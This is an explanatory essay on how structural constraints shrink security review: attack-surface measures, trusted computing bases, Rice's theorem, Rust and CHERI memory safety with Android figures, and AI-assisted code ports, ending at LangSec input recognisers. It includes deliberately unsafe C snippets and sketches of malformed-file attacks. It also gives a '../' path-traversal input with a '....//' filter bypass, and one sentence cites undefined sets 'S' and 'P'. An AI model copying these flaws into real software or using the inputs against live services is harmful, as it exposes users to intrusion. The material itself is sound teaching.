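# Shrinking the attack surface: how far structural constraints can replace smarter security reviewers

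## Why security review is open-ended, and what would make it narrow

Security review means deciding whether a program, or data that a program will process, is safe to accept. Software companies do it before a release, app stores do it before they list an app, and mail servers do a crude version on every attachment. The reviewer can be a person, a conventional program or an AI model. Most reviewers look for flaws by reading the code, feeding it awkward inputs, comparing it with known attacks and trying to think like an attacker.

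Another tradition in computer security tries to reduce the need for searching for vulnerabilities. It restricts the programming language, the input format or the powers of the running program, so that whole families of attack become impossible or do little harm. Such a restriction is a structural constraint, a property of the language, format or design that holds whatever the attacker tries. Engineers hope the remaining checks will be small enough for a simple program to perform.

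### The reviewer's problem

Suppose a web service accepts video files from strangers and returns thumbnails, the small still pictures that represent videos in a list. Its developers run it on ten million real videos and it never crashes. This is excellent evidence of reliability. If future videos resemble the ones tested, the developers can be about 95 percent confident that fewer than three in ten million will cause a crash.

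Past cases don't bound future ones when an attacker chooses the files, because attackers don't draw from the same pool as people uploading holiday films. If one malformed file among all possible files makes the service misbehave, attackers will send that file, as often as they like.

The reviewer also has to find nearly everything, while the attacker may need only one thing. Imagine a program with 200 exploitable flaws and a reviewer who catches each with 99 percent probability, independently of the rest. The chance of catching all 200 is 0.99 to the power of 200, or about 13 percent. Raise the reviewer's skill to 99.9 percent and there is still an 18 percent chance that at least one flaw survives. (Real attacks often need several flaws in a row, which helps the defender, but a single one can be enough.)

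The problem also changes as attackers adapt. Lampson (1990), in *Requirements and Technology for Computer Security*, compared security to ecology because when defenders repair one weakness, the adversary moves to another. The security team of Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, writes, "Attackers innovate, so defenders need to innovate just to keep pace."

To vouch for a system, a reviewer must foresee what an attacker could do with it. Attackers use whatever works, including the quirks of a compiler, the time a calculation takes and the habits of a tired administrator. No fixed body of knowledge covers all of these, so a reviewer needs roughly the breadth and inventiveness of the best attackers to keep up. If the best attackers are AI systems, the reviewer will have to be a comparably general AI system. That would complicate proposals such as Eric Drexler's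 to build advanced AI as a collection of narrow services.

The reply accepts most of this but denies that a reviewer must always foresee the attacker's ideas. That is necessary only where the system's safety depends on it, and designers have some control over where that is. Lampson's example is a lift. The software that schedules several lifts and answers calls from every floor may be very complicated, but the lift also has a simple brake that stops it if it exceeds a fixed speed, whatever else has gone wrong. To find out whether the lift can plunge down the shaft, an inspector can ignore the scheduling software and check only that the brake engages above that speed. This replaces an open-ended question, whether anything could make the lift run away, with one that a technician can settle in an afternoon.

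The reply holds only for dangers that a simple mechanism can stop. Some dangers in software have such a mechanism, but others don't yet. Some advocates of formal proof go further and argue that proving a program does its job already rules out a takeover. Even where a mechanism exists, checking that it stops one danger doesn't show that the system is safe from others. How far the reply applies therefore has to be judged separately for each family of dangers. It helps to measure how much of the system an attacker can touch and how much of it has to work.

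### What the attacker can touch

The glossary of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) defines a system's *attack surface* as the points on its boundary where an attacker can try to enter, cause an effect or extract data. The European Union's Cyber Resilience Act requires manufacturers to minimise attack surfaces. *A Mapping Analysis of Requirements Between the CRA and the GDPR* (2025) points out that the Act mentions external interfaces but gives no further detail. The paper also notes a slight conflict between this duty and the Act's requirement for security updates, since an update mechanism gives attackers another way in.

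Minimising something is easier with a number attached. Michael Howard had introduced the notion informally for Windows, and Pratyusa Manadhata and Jeannette Wing, with two co-authors, turned it into a systematic measure. Manadhata, Tan and colleagues (2007), in *An Approach to Measuring A System's Attack Surface*, define the surface as three sets:

- M, the methods (functions) that receive data from outside the system or send data out;
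- C, the channels, such as network sockets, over which outsiders connect;
- I, the untrusted data items, which are lasting objects such as files, cookies or database records that both the system and the attacker can reach.

A plain count would mislead, because a function running as root, the all-powerful administrator account on a Unix machine, offers an attacker more than one running as an ordinary user. So each item gets a weight, its damage potential divided by the effort of reaching it. For a method, damage potential depends on the privilege it runs with. For a channel it depends on the protocol, and for a data item on its type. Effort depends on the access rights an attacker must first acquire. Writing d for damage potential and e for effort, the measure is a triple of sums:

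⟨ Σ d(m)/e(m) over M, Σ d(c)/e(c) over C, Σ d(i)/e(i) over I ⟩

Here is the calculation for an invented version of the thumbnail service, which has a website and an older feature that lets customers upload by FTP, a file-transfer protocol from the 1970s. The counts are made up, but the weights are the ones Manadhata and colleagues used for two mail servers. Root privilege has a weight of 5 and an ordinary user's privilege has a weight of 3. Effort has a weight of 1 where no login is needed, 3 for a login, and 4 for a login on the machine itself.

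| Part of the service | Number | Damage ÷ effort | Contribution |
|---|---|---|---|
| Methods: web upload and decoding, user privilege, no login | 10 | 3 ÷ 1 | 30 |
| Methods: account settings, user privilege, login | 6 | 3 ÷ 3 | 6 |
| Methods: FTP upload, root privilege, no login | 8 | 5 ÷ 1 | 40 |
| Channel: web, open to anyone | 1 | 1 ÷ 1 | 1 |
| Channel: local database connection, local login | 1 | 1 ÷ 4 | 0.25 |
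| Channel: FTP, open to anyone | 1 | 1 ÷ 1 | 1 |
| Data: files that need a login | 9 | 1 ÷ 3 | 3 |
| Data: files open to anyone | 3 | 1 ÷ 1 | 3 |
| Data: FTP drop files, open to anyone | 4 | 1 ÷ 1 | 4 |

The service measures ⟨76, 2.25, 10⟩ with FTP and ⟨36, 1.25, 6⟩ without it. FTP accounts for a third of the methods but more than half of their weight, because it runs as root and anyone can reach it. If customers insist on keeping it, running it as an ordinary user would cut its contribution to the first figure from 40 to 24.

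The weights are a matter of judgement, and they can decide the result. Manadhata and colleagues compared two FTP servers, ProFTPD and Wu-FTPD, which have almost the same number of entry and exit points (107 and 109). They varied the numerical gap between one level of privilege or access and the next. With a gap of 2 for privilege and 17 for access, Wu-FTPD scored worse, at 444.6 against 349.7. With gaps of 17 and 6, ProFTPD scored worse, at 1,785.3 against 1,672.1. The ranking stayed the same under nearly any choice of weights only when one program had far more entry and exit points than the other, as with the two mail servers. The measure is a fair guide to whether a change to one system has exposed more or less of it, but a poor way to choose between two similar products.

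More fundamentally, the measure ignores the quality of the code. Manadhata and colleagues state that a large surface need not contain many flaws, nor a small one few. If the developers rewrote the whole thumbnail service in a language that excludes memory errors, all three numbers could stay the same. The measure also leaves out side channels, which leak information through timing or power use rather than through the ordinary sending or receiving of data.

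Later work has kept the framework and tried to fill its gaps. *Measuring Security in 5G and Future Networks* (2025) still builds its score from entry points, channels and data. *Security Engineering of OpenClaw* (2026), on an AI agent that can install new skills and run tools, adds two quantities. The first is the probability that an attack on each interface succeeds, estimated through repeated trials. The second is the factor by which a successful attack raises the attacker's privilege. These additions are more informative about present danger, but the probability holds for a specified level of attacker capability, and the paper has a separate term for how steeply exposure rises as that capability grows. Somebody still has to guess how capable the attackers will be, which makes the assessment open-ended again. The 2007 measure is cruder, but using it requires no assumption about the attacker's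 skill.

### What has to work

The trusted computing base is the hardware and software that must be correct for a security guarantee to hold. NIST's *trusted computing base (TCB)* entry describes it as all the protection mechanisms that enforce a security policy. Lampson's definition is easier to apply. It starts from the specification, which states precisely what the system must do or must never do. Any component the system needs to meet the specification is trusted, and so is everything that component depends on.

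A component is "trusted" here if its failure would break the guarantee, whether or not anyone has good reason to rely on it. The trusted base also includes everything those components depend on, so it is usually larger than people expect. A fifty-line program that calls a video library of half a million lines has a trusted base of at least 500,050 lines, not counting the operating system and the processor.

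Lampson advises keeping the base small by moving security decisions into a simple core and leaving everything else outside. One of his examples is a company's purchasing system. Staff may write orders in a word processor too large and complicated for anyone to review with confidence. But if a simple program displays the finished order and asks the user to confirm it, only that program and what it runs on have to be right. A fault in the word processor can still produce a wrong order, but the user sees the order before it goes out. Security then also depends on the user, and Lampson says a full accounting includes people, power supplies and locked doors.

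The attack surface and the trusted base can shrink separately. Closing the FTP port removes a way in but leaves the video decoder as critical as before. Isolating the decoder so that its failure harms nobody takes it out of the trusted base, though strangers can still send it files.

### Why no checker can decide everything

A smaller surface and a smaller base leave the reviewer with less code to judge, but no program can determine for all code whether it will misbehave. *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems* (Rice, 1953) proves what is now called Rice's theorem, which states that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether the program has a given non-trivial behavioural property. A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others don't, and behavioural if it concerns what the program does rather than how its text looks. For example, "sometimes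 deletes the user's files" is a behavioural property, while "contains the word *delete*" is a property of the text that any editor can search for.

An example shows how the proof works. Suppose a checker could correctly report, for every program, whether it will ever delete the user's files. Take any program D, and write a new program that first runs D, sealed off so that D cannot touch any files itself, and then deletes the user's files. The new program deletes the files if and only if D finishes, so we could use the checker to find out whether D finishes. But Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can determine this for every program (the halting problem), so the checker cannot exist. Teaching slides from Brown University give the general version, with an arbitrary behaviour in place of the deletion.

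Strictly, the theorem concerns idealised computers with unlimited memory. A real machine has finitely many states, so a checker could in principle go through them all. But one megabyte of memory allows about 2 to the power of 8 million states, which is too many to check in practice.

Rice's theorem applies to every reviewer that is an algorithm, including an AI model, however intelligent. A more intelligent reviewer will judge more programs correctly, perhaps nearly all the programs that people write in good faith, but no algorithm can return the right answer for every program an adversary might submit.

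Rice's theorem implies that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether it behaves safely. But a designer can choose a smaller set of safe programs whose membership an algorithm can decide. A checker that accepts only programs in this set never accepts an unsafe one, though it also rejects some safe ones.

A toy version is the rule "reject any program whose text contains a call to the delete function", which a text search can enforce. The rule rejects some harmless programs, such as one where the call is in a branch that never runs, but the author can remove the unused line and resubmit. In open-ended review, the reviewer has to work out whether whatever the author wrote is safe. A conservative rule shifts that work to the author, who has to write the program so that a simple checker can tell it is safe. The toy rule works only if the language offers no other way to delete a file.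 If there is another way, S is no longer inside P and the guarantee is lost.

The same approach works for data. A service can accept only files in a format simple enough for a short program to check completely, and refuse all others, including some harmless ones.

The Rust Book, the standard introduction to the programming language Rust, defends the trade by arguing that if the compiler accepted an incorrect program, nobody could rely on its guarantees, whereas rejecting a correct one only inconveniences the programmer. That is true, but people will find a way to switch off a checker that rejects too much good work. Lampson describes a traffic light whose safety rule is that two conflicting roads never get green together. A light that stays red in every direction satisfies the rule, but drivers soon start to ignore it. Whether a conservative check is practical therefore depends on how much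 useful software or data fits inside S, or can fit after a tolerable amount of rewriting.

### Three tests of a narrow task

A review task is narrow when it has a fixed question and a mechanical test, and the reviewer doesn't have to predict what an attacker will think of. Three criteria distinguish such tasks from ones that only look narrow.

The check must be mechanical, meaning that a program or a person following written rules can carry it out, and any two of them will reach the same verdict. One example is checking whether a file contains exactly as many bytes as its header declares. Asking whether code looks suspicious is not a mechanical check, even when a language model answers in a second, because no rule determines the right answer.

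The verdict must hold however ingenious the attacker is. Much existing security software fails this requirement. A virus scanner that compares files with a list of known malicious patterns is entirely mechanical, but an attacker can keep altering a file until no pattern matches. The toy rule about deletion meets the requirement if its assumption about the language is true. Knowing the full rule then doesn't help an attacker, because no program that passes can delete files.

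The amount that has to be trusted must also be small. Even with a watertight rule, a mechanical check is only as reliable as the program that performs it and whatever that program relies on. If the checker is a million lines long, the reviewer has the same problem with the checker as with the original code.

These are matters of degree, and a rule can be useful without passing all three. For example, Chromium's *The Rule Of 2* tells developers that a piece of code may combine at most two of three things: untrustworthy input, an implementation language without memory safety, and high privilege. (A memory-safe program reads and writes only memory it is entitled to use, while that memory is still valid.) The Chrome security team will generally not approve a change that combines all three. Applying the rule doesn't require anyone to think of an attack, though it still takes some judgement because,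 as Chromium concedes, high privilege is a relative term. Code that obeys the rule can still have bugs, but the rule limits how bad they are likely to be.

### The thumbnail service at its worst

Suppose now that the developers have dropped FTP but written the thumbnail service in C, a fast language without memory safety, and that they run it with the full privileges of an ordinary user account. The service then has all three of the ingredients that the Rule of 2 forbids together. Chromium's guidance names video frames among the kinds of data that are error-prone to decode, and adds that the risk grows whenever code branches on the values of the bytes it is reading. A video decoder does so constantly. Its reviewer has to worry about at least the following:

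- A file declares a block of 1,000 bytes and supplies 4,000. If the code trusts the declaration, the surplus overwrites whatever lies next in memory, and a skilled attacker can sometimes turn that into running code of their own.
- A file declares a picture 65,536 pixels wide and 65,536 high. Multiplied as 32-bit numbers these give exactly zero, so the program reserves no memory and then starts writing a picture into it.
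- A frame refers back to an earlier frame whose memory the decoder has already released and reused for something else.
- A file of a few kilobytes unpacks into a picture that exhausts the machine's memory, or sends the decoder into a loop that never ends.
- Some video formats let a file point to other files or network addresses. The decoder may obligingly open a private document and turn it into a thumbnail.
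- An uploaded file's name contains "../", the notation for "one folder up", and the service saves the file somewhere it should not.
- The service sends one customer a thumbnail of another customer's video. Every operation is legal and no memory goes wrong; the program has simply broken its own rules.
- The decoding library comes from outside the company, and its next update may contain a new mistake, or something worse.

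Full user privileges make the memory faults much more serious. An attacker who takes over the decoder can do anything that account can do, including reading every stored video, copying passwords and keys, connecting to other machines on the company's network, and leaving a program behind for later. The decoder needs almost none of this access, because it only has to read one file and produce one small picture.

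A reviewer could check these eight items carefully and approve the service, but they would have no way of knowing whether the list was complete.

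## Memory-safe languages: removing a class of fault at compile time

Three of the eight worries about the thumbnail service are memory faults: the file that holds more data than it declares, the picture whose dimensions multiply to zero, and the earlier frame that the decoder reads after freeing its memory. Such faults are common in C and C++, the languages behind most operating systems, browsers and video decoders. Google says they typically account for 70 percent of all vulnerabilities across the industry, and tend to be more severe than other kinds and easier to reach remotely.

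### Two faults in a few lines of C

When a C program asks for a block of memory, it gets back a pointer, which is just the address where the block starts. The pointer doesn't record how long the block is or whether it is still in use. A *buffer overflow* happens when the program writes past the end:

```c
char *block = malloc(declared_size);     /* the header declares 1,000 bytes */
memcpy(block, file_data, actual_size);   /* the file contains 4,000 */
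```

The extra 3,000 bytes might overwrite part of another picture. They might also overwrite a value that determines which instructions the processor runs next, which is how a malformed video can let an attacker take control.

A *use-after-free* happens when the program goes back to memory it has already given up:

```c
struct frame *previous = frames[0];
free(frames[0]);
show(previous);
```

After `free`, the program may reuse that memory for something else, such as data from the attacker's file. But `previous` still holds the old address, so `show` treats the new contents as a frame. The mistake is obvious when the three lines are together, but in a real decoder they may be in three different files, and `free` may run only when an unusual frame arrives.

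### Checks, collectors and owners

A memory-safe language prevents overflows by storing the length of each block next to its address and checking every index against that length. If the index is too large, the program stops. The check happens while the program runs because the compiler usually can't predict the index.

*Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes a memory error that a team carried over from Zig to Rust. Bun runs JavaScript outside a web browser, and until 2026 most of it was written in Zig, which leaves memory management to the programmer much as C does. On macOS and Linux, its developers compiled it without bounds checks. The code contained an off-by-one error that could write one place past the end of a list. The Rust version had the same error, and a wrong setting made it reachable in ordinary projects, but the program stopped with an error message instead of writing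 past the end. That is much better than letting an attacker take over, though an attacker who can stop a service at will can still do damage.

Bounds checks don't prevent use-after-free, because an index can still be valid after the memory has been freed. Java, Go, JavaScript and Python solve this with a *garbage collector*, a part of the language's runtime system that frees memory so the programmer doesn't have to. It periodically works out which blocks the program can still reach and reclaims the rest. As long as `previous` refers to a frame, the frame stays. The collector uses memory and processor time, and it may pause the program at an awkward moment, so engineers rarely use one in an operating system's core or in firmware.

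Rust manages without a collector because its compiler works out in advance when the program can release each piece of memory. Every value has exactly one owner, usually a variable. When the owner goes out of use, the program releases the memory automatically. A function can take over a value, after which the caller can no longer use it, or it can *borrow* the value through a reference and leave the ownership where it was. Two rules govern borrowing:

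- No reference may outlive the value it refers to.
- At any moment a value can have any number of read-only references, or one reference that allows changes, but not both.

The compiler rejects this example:

```rust
let mut frames = vec![first_frame];   // line 1
let previous = &frames[0];            // line 2
frames.push(second_frame);            // line 3
show(previous);                       // line 4
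```

Line 1 makes `frames` the owner of a mutable list containing one frame. In line 2, `previous` borrows that frame as read-only. Line 3 adds another frame with `push`, which needs a mutable reference to the list. Because line 4 uses `previous`, the borrow from line 2 is still active at line 3, so the compiler rejects line 3 with the message "cannot borrow `frames` as mutable because it is also borrowed as immutable".

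Adding a frame at the end of the list can invalidate a reference to the one at the start, because a list of this kind occupies one continuous block of memory. If the block is full, `push` moves the whole list to a bigger block and releases the old one, which would leave `previous` pointing at released memory. The equivalent C++ compiles without errors or warnings. Sumner lists a very similar fault among those the Bun team fixed in its last Zig version, where a table of network streams could reorganise itself while other code still held pointers into it.

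Swapping lines 3 and 4 satisfies the compiler because the loan then ends before the list changes, and copying the frame would also work. The compiler would reject the original even if the list had plenty of spare room and the program were harmless, as conservative checks usually reject some harmless programs. But the check is fully mechanical, and nothing an attacker sends later can change its result. It also scales well, because each function's declaration specifies what the function borrows and what it takes ownership of, so the compiler can examine one function at a time. Its main weakness is that it relies on the Rust compiler and standard library, which are large programs that can have faults of their own.

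CHERI, a processor design from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, enforces similar limits in hardware, so existing C code can benefit without a rewrite, though developers have to recompile it and usually adjust some of it. A CHERI pointer contains an address, the bounds of its memory block and a set of permissions. A hidden tag lets the processor detect a pointer that the program has forged or corrupted. This makes the pointer a capability, an unforgeable reference that also grants the right to use what it names. If the code above tried to copy 4,000 bytes into a block of 1,000, the processor would halt it at byte 1,001. Preventing use-after-free requires extra software that finds and disables old pointers before the program reuses the memory. CHERI leaves the faults in the code and makes them much less dangerous, but only on machines with the new processors.

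### What happened on Android

The best evidence on the effect of changing languages comes from Android, Google's phone operating system. Around 2019, its developers began to favour memory-safe languages for new code while leaving most of the old C and C++ alone. Memory faults made up 76 percent of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019. Google put the share at 24 percent for 2024, and *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) put it below 20 percent for 2025. Vander Stoep, who works on Android security, published two months before the year ended, but Google allows 90 days for a patch, so most of the year's cases were already known.

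The share of vulnerabilities that involve memory safety can fall because other kinds have multiplied, so the counts matter too. Google had recorded 27 memory-safety vulnerabilities by September 2024, from which it estimated 36 for the full year. If those were 24 percent of the total, there were about 150 vulnerabilities in all. The yearly count has fallen along with the share, apart from a slight rise in 2023, when people reported unusually many vulnerabilities. Google was also making its old C and C++ safer during these years, which it acknowledges may explain part of the improvement.

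The number of vulnerabilities per line better reflects the effect of the language itself. Google has found one potential memory-safety vulnerability in Android's roughly 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million lines. Its historical figure for C and C++ is about 1,000 per million lines, which is 5,000 times the Rust rate, though Vander Stoep claims only a difference of "more than 1000x".

The caution is sensible, because a rate based on a single case is very uncertain. By the standard calculation for rare events, finding one vulnerability is compatible with an expected number as high as 5.6, or 1.1 per million lines, which would be about 900 times lower than the figure for C and C++. The Rust code is also young, so researchers have had less time to search it. If they have found only a quarter of its vulnerabilities, the difference would shrink from about 900-fold to a little over 200-fold.

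The components may differ too. Vander Stoep gives no breakdown by component, and Rust would look safer than it is if Google had used it mainly for simple, low-risk services. But Google has also used it in code that attackers often target. The one potential vulnerability was in an image decoder, and Chromium now uses Rust to process PNG images and web fonts. Differences in difficulty or skill seem unlikely to explain a factor of several hundred, especially since it is clear how the compiler prevents these faults.

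Google's other figures are less certain. A *rollback* is the withdrawal of an accepted change, usually because it broke something. For medium and large changes, the rollback rate in Rust is about a quarter of the rate in C++. Rust changes also spend about 25 percent less time in code review and need about 20 percent fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size. The difference in review time is clearest for the largest changes.

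Vander Stoep's figures cover only Android's own platform developers, many of whom write both Rust and C++, and compare changes within the same size class. This partly answers the objection that Rust simply has better programmers, but it doesn't account for the age of the code being changed. A developer adding to a new Rust component has less old behaviour to break than one altering a C++ component that much of the system depends on. That could account for a good deal of the fourfold difference. Separating the effect of language from the effect of age would take a comparison of Rust and C++ components of the same age, which Vander Stoep doesn't report.

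Even if Rust accounts for the whole 25 percent, most of the reviewing remains. Reviewers still have to work out whether a change does what its author intended, and that usually has nothing to do with memory.

### Unsafe code

Some jobs are beyond what the Rust compiler can verify, such as controlling hardware or calling a library in C. For these, a programmer can mark a block with the word `unsafe` and take responsibility for it. Here is a small example, which reads a pixel without a bounds check to save time:

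```rust
// SAFETY: i is always smaller than pixels.len()
let p = unsafe { *pixels.get_unchecked(i) };
```

The `unsafe` block permits a few extra operations, but the rest of Rust's rules still apply inside it. A text search finds every such block in a program, though judging the code inside takes some skill. Here the comment gives the condition to confirm. If `i` comes from a stored value that other functions can change, the reviewer has to read those functions too. Programmers limit this extra reading by making the value private to one small module, so that code elsewhere can't break the condition.

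About 4 percent of Android's Rust, or roughly 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. If these lines were as faulty as Google's C and C++, they would contain about 200 memory-safety vulnerabilities, but Google has found one. Vander Stoep isn't sure why the number is so low, but suggests that the checks Rust still applies inside unsafe blocks, enclosing unsafe code in small modules, and extra attention from reviewers all help.

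The one case, CVE-2025-48530, was a buffer overflow in unsafe code in CrabbyAVIF, a library for the AVIF image format. Google fixed it before any public release. It would have been hard to exploit on most Android phones anyway, because Android's default memory allocator, Scudo, puts inaccessible regions called guard pages around large blocks of memory. A write that runs off the end of a block hits a guard page and crashes the program. The crash also helped Google find the fault, but the crash reports didn't make clear that an overflow was responsible, which slowed the response. Some manufacturers don't use Scudo, and Google is trying to make it mandatory.

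*Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes a more worrying example, which a new model from the AI company Anthropic found in April 2026 when asked to look for vulnerabilities in real software. The fault was in a virtual machine monitor, the program that lets several customers share a physical computer in a data centre and keeps them apart. The monitor was written in a memory-safe language, but the fault was in an unsafe operation, of a kind every such monitor needs because it deals directly with hardware. A malicious customer could use the fault to write outside the permitted memory on the shared machine. Carlini and colleagues judged that this could easily crash the host, but the model tried and failed to turn it into a working takeover.

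They didn't name the program because its developers hadn't yet fixed the fault. On the same day, AWS, Amazon's cloud division, published *CVE-2026-5747* (2026), which describes an out-of-bounds write in Firecracker, a virtual machine monitor written in Rust, and credits Anthropic with reporting it. The two may well be the same fault, although AWS had a fix ready and neither account connects them. The Firecracker fault affected an optional feature that is off by default, and no AWS service was vulnerable.

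Anthropic (2026) keeps a public ledger of flaws that its models have found in open-source software. About two thirds of the published entries are out-of-bounds accesses or uses after free, nearly all in C and C++ projects. The ledger also includes the Firecracker fault and a use-after-free in a Rust file in Suricata, a network intrusion detector. Carlini and colleagues concentrated on memory faults, partly because an automatic tool can confirm them, so the ledger isn't a fair comparison between languages. But it does show that AI reviewers are searching the unsafe parts of Rust programs and finding flaws there.

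### What to do about old code

Android's share of memory faults fell even though most of its code was still in C and C++. The reason is that vulnerabilities thin out as code ages, because people find them and fix them. Google models this as exponential decay. If a vulnerability survives for λ years on average, then code that is t years old has a density of

density in new code × e^(−t/λ)

Google's simulation uses an average vulnerability lifetime (λ) of 2.5 years, so five-year-old code has e^(−2) times the vulnerability density of new code, or 7.4 times lower. An academic study of open-source software found longer lifetimes, which reduce the factor to 3.4.

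Suppose a team has long been adding 100,000 lines of C++ a year, at Google's historical rate of one vulnerability per thousand lines. It adds 100 vulnerabilities a year, and with a λ of 2.5 years, the number still undiscovered levels off at about 250. If the team then writes all its new code in Rust and changes the C++ only to fix bugs, about 34 of those 250 remain after five years, even though nobody has rewritten the old code in Rust. In Google's simulation, which assumes a gradual switch over ten years, the number of vulnerabilities falls even while the total amount of C++ keeps growing.

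For a team with limited time, this is a strong argument for changing the language of new code first. It is a weaker argument for leaving old code alone, because the curve includes only vulnerabilities that have been found.

Carlini and colleagues' results suggest that there are plenty of these. Their model found a 27-year-old flaw in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security. It also found a 16-year-old flaw in FFmpeg, the library that most large services use to process video and that the thumbnail service would likely use too. Human reviewers had missed this flaw, which was in the decoder for H.264, a very common video format. So had fuzzers, which are programs that feed software millions of random inputs and watch for crashes. Several hundred runs over FFmpeg cost about $10,000 and also turned up several other important vulnerabilities. Old code can have many vulnerabilities in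 total even if it has few per line, and their rarity protects it less when searching for them costs so little.

Flaws take longer to fix than to find. By 2 November 2026 Anthropic had reported 5,087 flaws to open-source maintainers and knew of fixes for 629. Video decoding is still a weak point on Android too. The Hacker News' *Google Fixes Android Video Decoder and IMS Flaws That Could Allow RCE* (2026) covers a December update that fixed 85 flaws, including one in a video decoder that could let an attacker run code on a phone without its owner doing anything.

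One answer is to replace only the riskiest old parts. Google's *Bringing Rust to the Pixel Baseband* describes how engineers added a Rust component to the Pixel 10 phone's modem firmware to process replies from the Domain Name System, which translates domain names into internet addresses. The rest of the firmware could stay as it was. A team can also run old code in a sandbox, which limits the harm its faults can do. In 2026, it also became practical to translate whole programs with AI.

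### Rewriting old code with AI

Bun is the most detailed public example. It had 535,496 lines of Zig, and Sumner, its creator, used an AI model to port them to Rust in 11 days in May 2026, at a cost of about $165,000. Sumner estimates that three engineers would have needed a year. (Anthropic owns Bun and made the model, so Sumner isn't a neutral witness, but users can run both versions.)

The port relied heavily on mechanical checks. Sumner and the model first wrote a guide to translating Zig patterns into Rust and a table of how long each stored piece of data had to last. Up to 64 copies of the model then worked in parallel. For each file, one copy wrote the Rust, and two others, which saw only the changes, looked for reasons it was wrong. The code then had to compile without errors and pass Bun's test suite, which makes over a million checks and didn't need translating because it was in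 TypeScript. Sumner merged the port once every test passed on every platform.

How much unsafe code such a port keeps depends mostly on how it was made. Older tools such as c2rust translate C line by line using fixed rules. The 2026 paper on *AdaTrans*, a system that translates C with an AI model, used c2rust as a comparison and found that nearly all of c2rust's output was in unsafe blocks. *Mostly Automatic Translation of Language Interpreters from C to Safe Rust* (2026) explains that these tools preserve the structure of the original. C programs often share pointers in ways that Rust's borrowing rules forbid, so a translation that keeps that structure has to be unsafe. An AI model can reorganise the code instead.

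| Rust code | Share of lines in unsafe blocks |
|---|---|
| C programs translated by c2rust | 97.94% |
| C programs translated by AdaTrans | under 0.1% |
| Bun, July 2026 | about 3.5% (27,000 of 780,000) |
| Android, mostly new code | about 4% |

*AdaTrans* (2026) attributes its low figure to a collection of repair templates that steer the model towards safe code, but the model itself is probably the main reason. In the same experiment, 1.05 percent of the programs from a model without the templates contained any unsafe code, against 1.19 percent for AdaTrans. Both percentages cover only translations that passed validation, which may have been the easier programs.

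Bun has more unsafe code because it depends on large C and C++ libraries, including its JavaScript engine, and every call into them needs an unsafe block. Bun's *Rust codebase audit* (2026), which an AI produced a week after the merge, counted 13,365 unsafe blocks. It estimated that developers could convert about 9,300 to safe code and would have to keep about 4,000.

Counts like these can mislead. *From C to Idiomatic Rust* (2026) describes a project in which developers and AI agents turned 12,500 lines of C into 10,300 lines of Rust in 37 working hours. They cut the unsafe blocks in the client portion from about 86 to 40. But they chose not to use the raw count to measure progress, because good translation often replaces one large unsafe function with several small unsafe blocks, which makes the code safer but raises the count.

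The opposite error, presenting an unsafe function as safe, is more dangerous. Bun's audit found functions like this in the port, which safe code could misuse to corrupt memory. Anyone reviewing only the code that calls these functions would see nothing marked as unsafe. The audit prioritized fixing them over reducing the count.

Ports also introduce new faults. In one case, the Rust code passed a block of memory to a C library that would need it a moment later. Rust's automatic cleanup then released the block, because the compiler could not detect that the library still needed it. This created a use-after-free that was not in the original, and the code compiled without errors. The reviewing copies caught the fault before the merge.

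The 19 known regressions that got through were mostly of another kind. Many came from expressions that look the same in Zig and Rust but behave differently. For example, the Zig code did some necessary work inside an `assert`, a check that a condition holds. The port used Rust's `debug_assert!`, which the compiler removes from release versions along with the work inside it, so the feature worked in testing but broke for users. Bun's developers have fixed all 19. Sumner counts 128 bugs in the last Zig version that the Rust version fixes, from crashes and memory leaks to help text in the wrong colour.

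Security review also continued after the port. By July the team had put the Rust code through 11 rounds of AI security review. It had also run Bun's parsers, which interpret incoming text, about 100 billion times on generated inputs, leading to around 15 fixes.

### The thumbnail service in Rust

Suppose the service's developers port their decoder to safe Rust. The file with 4,000 bytes in a block of 1,000 and the picture that is 65,536 pixels square can no longer overwrite anything. The picture's multiplication still gives zero in a release build, because Rust doesn't check for overflow there by default, but the first attempt to store a pixel fails its bounds check and the decoder stops.

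In the reused-frame case, the compiler rejects code that releases a frame's memory while the decoder still holds a reference to it. Many decoders, however, keep a fixed pool of frames and refer to them by number. A malformed video could then cause a read of frame 3 after the decoder has filled it with a different picture. Every memory access is legal, but the thumbnail may show part of someone else's video.

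The other five worries remain, because none of them depends on a memory fault. For example, a malicious library update can do damage even if it is written entirely in safe Rust. Several of the five arise because the service accepts a file it could have refused.

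## Restricted input formats: rejecting bad data before it is processed

Any program that accepts untrusted files has to decide which ones to process, but most programs don't make that decision in one place. A typical decoder reads a few bytes, checks them, acts on them and then reads more. If it finds halfway through that the file is invalid, it has already acted on the first half.

Language-theoretic security, or LangSec, is a school of thought that blames this habit for much of the insecurity of modern software. *The Halting Problems of Network Stack Insecurity* (Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues, 2011) set out its main ideas, and twelve workshops have built on them since 2014. The paper proposes that designers treat a program's valid inputs as a formal language, meaning a precisely defined set of strings. A recogniser, the code that decides whether an input belongs to that set, should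 examine the whole input and accept or reject it before any other code acts on it.

The names of uploaded files are easy to restrict. On the thumbnail service, a name containing "../" could make the service save a file in the wrong folder. A recogniser could prevent this by accepting only names made of 1 to 64 letters or digits followed by ".mp4". No such name contains a slash, so whoever writes the rule doesn't need to know about the "../" trick, or any other trick that relies on unusual characters. Searching for "../" and deleting it is less reliable, because an attacker could write "....//", which becomes "../" once the filter has removed the middle.

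### From regular to Turing-complete

The rule for a valid video file is longer than the rule for a valid file name, and some rules are much harder to check than others. In the 1950s the linguist Noam Chomsky sorted languages into classes, and computer scientists now define each class by how powerful a machine must be to recognise its languages.

A program can recognise a *regular* language with a fixed amount of memory. One example is "one or more digits, then px", which matches "640px". The program reads one character at a time and only has to track whether it has read nothing, some digits, the "p" or the full "px". Web addresses are also regular, although the full rule for them is very long.

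A *context-free* language allows nesting to any depth. In the language of balanced brackets, for example, "([]())" is valid and "([)]" isn't. Because the nesting has no limit, a fixed amount of memory isn't enough, so the recogniser keeps a stack. It puts each opening bracket on top of the stack and removes it when the matching closing bracket arrives. JSON, a common text format for data, has this nested structure. A recogniser for brackets has only one possible move at each step, which makes the language *deterministic* context-free. The language of strings that read the same in both directions, such as "abba", is context-free but not deterministic, because the recogniser would have to guess where the middle is.

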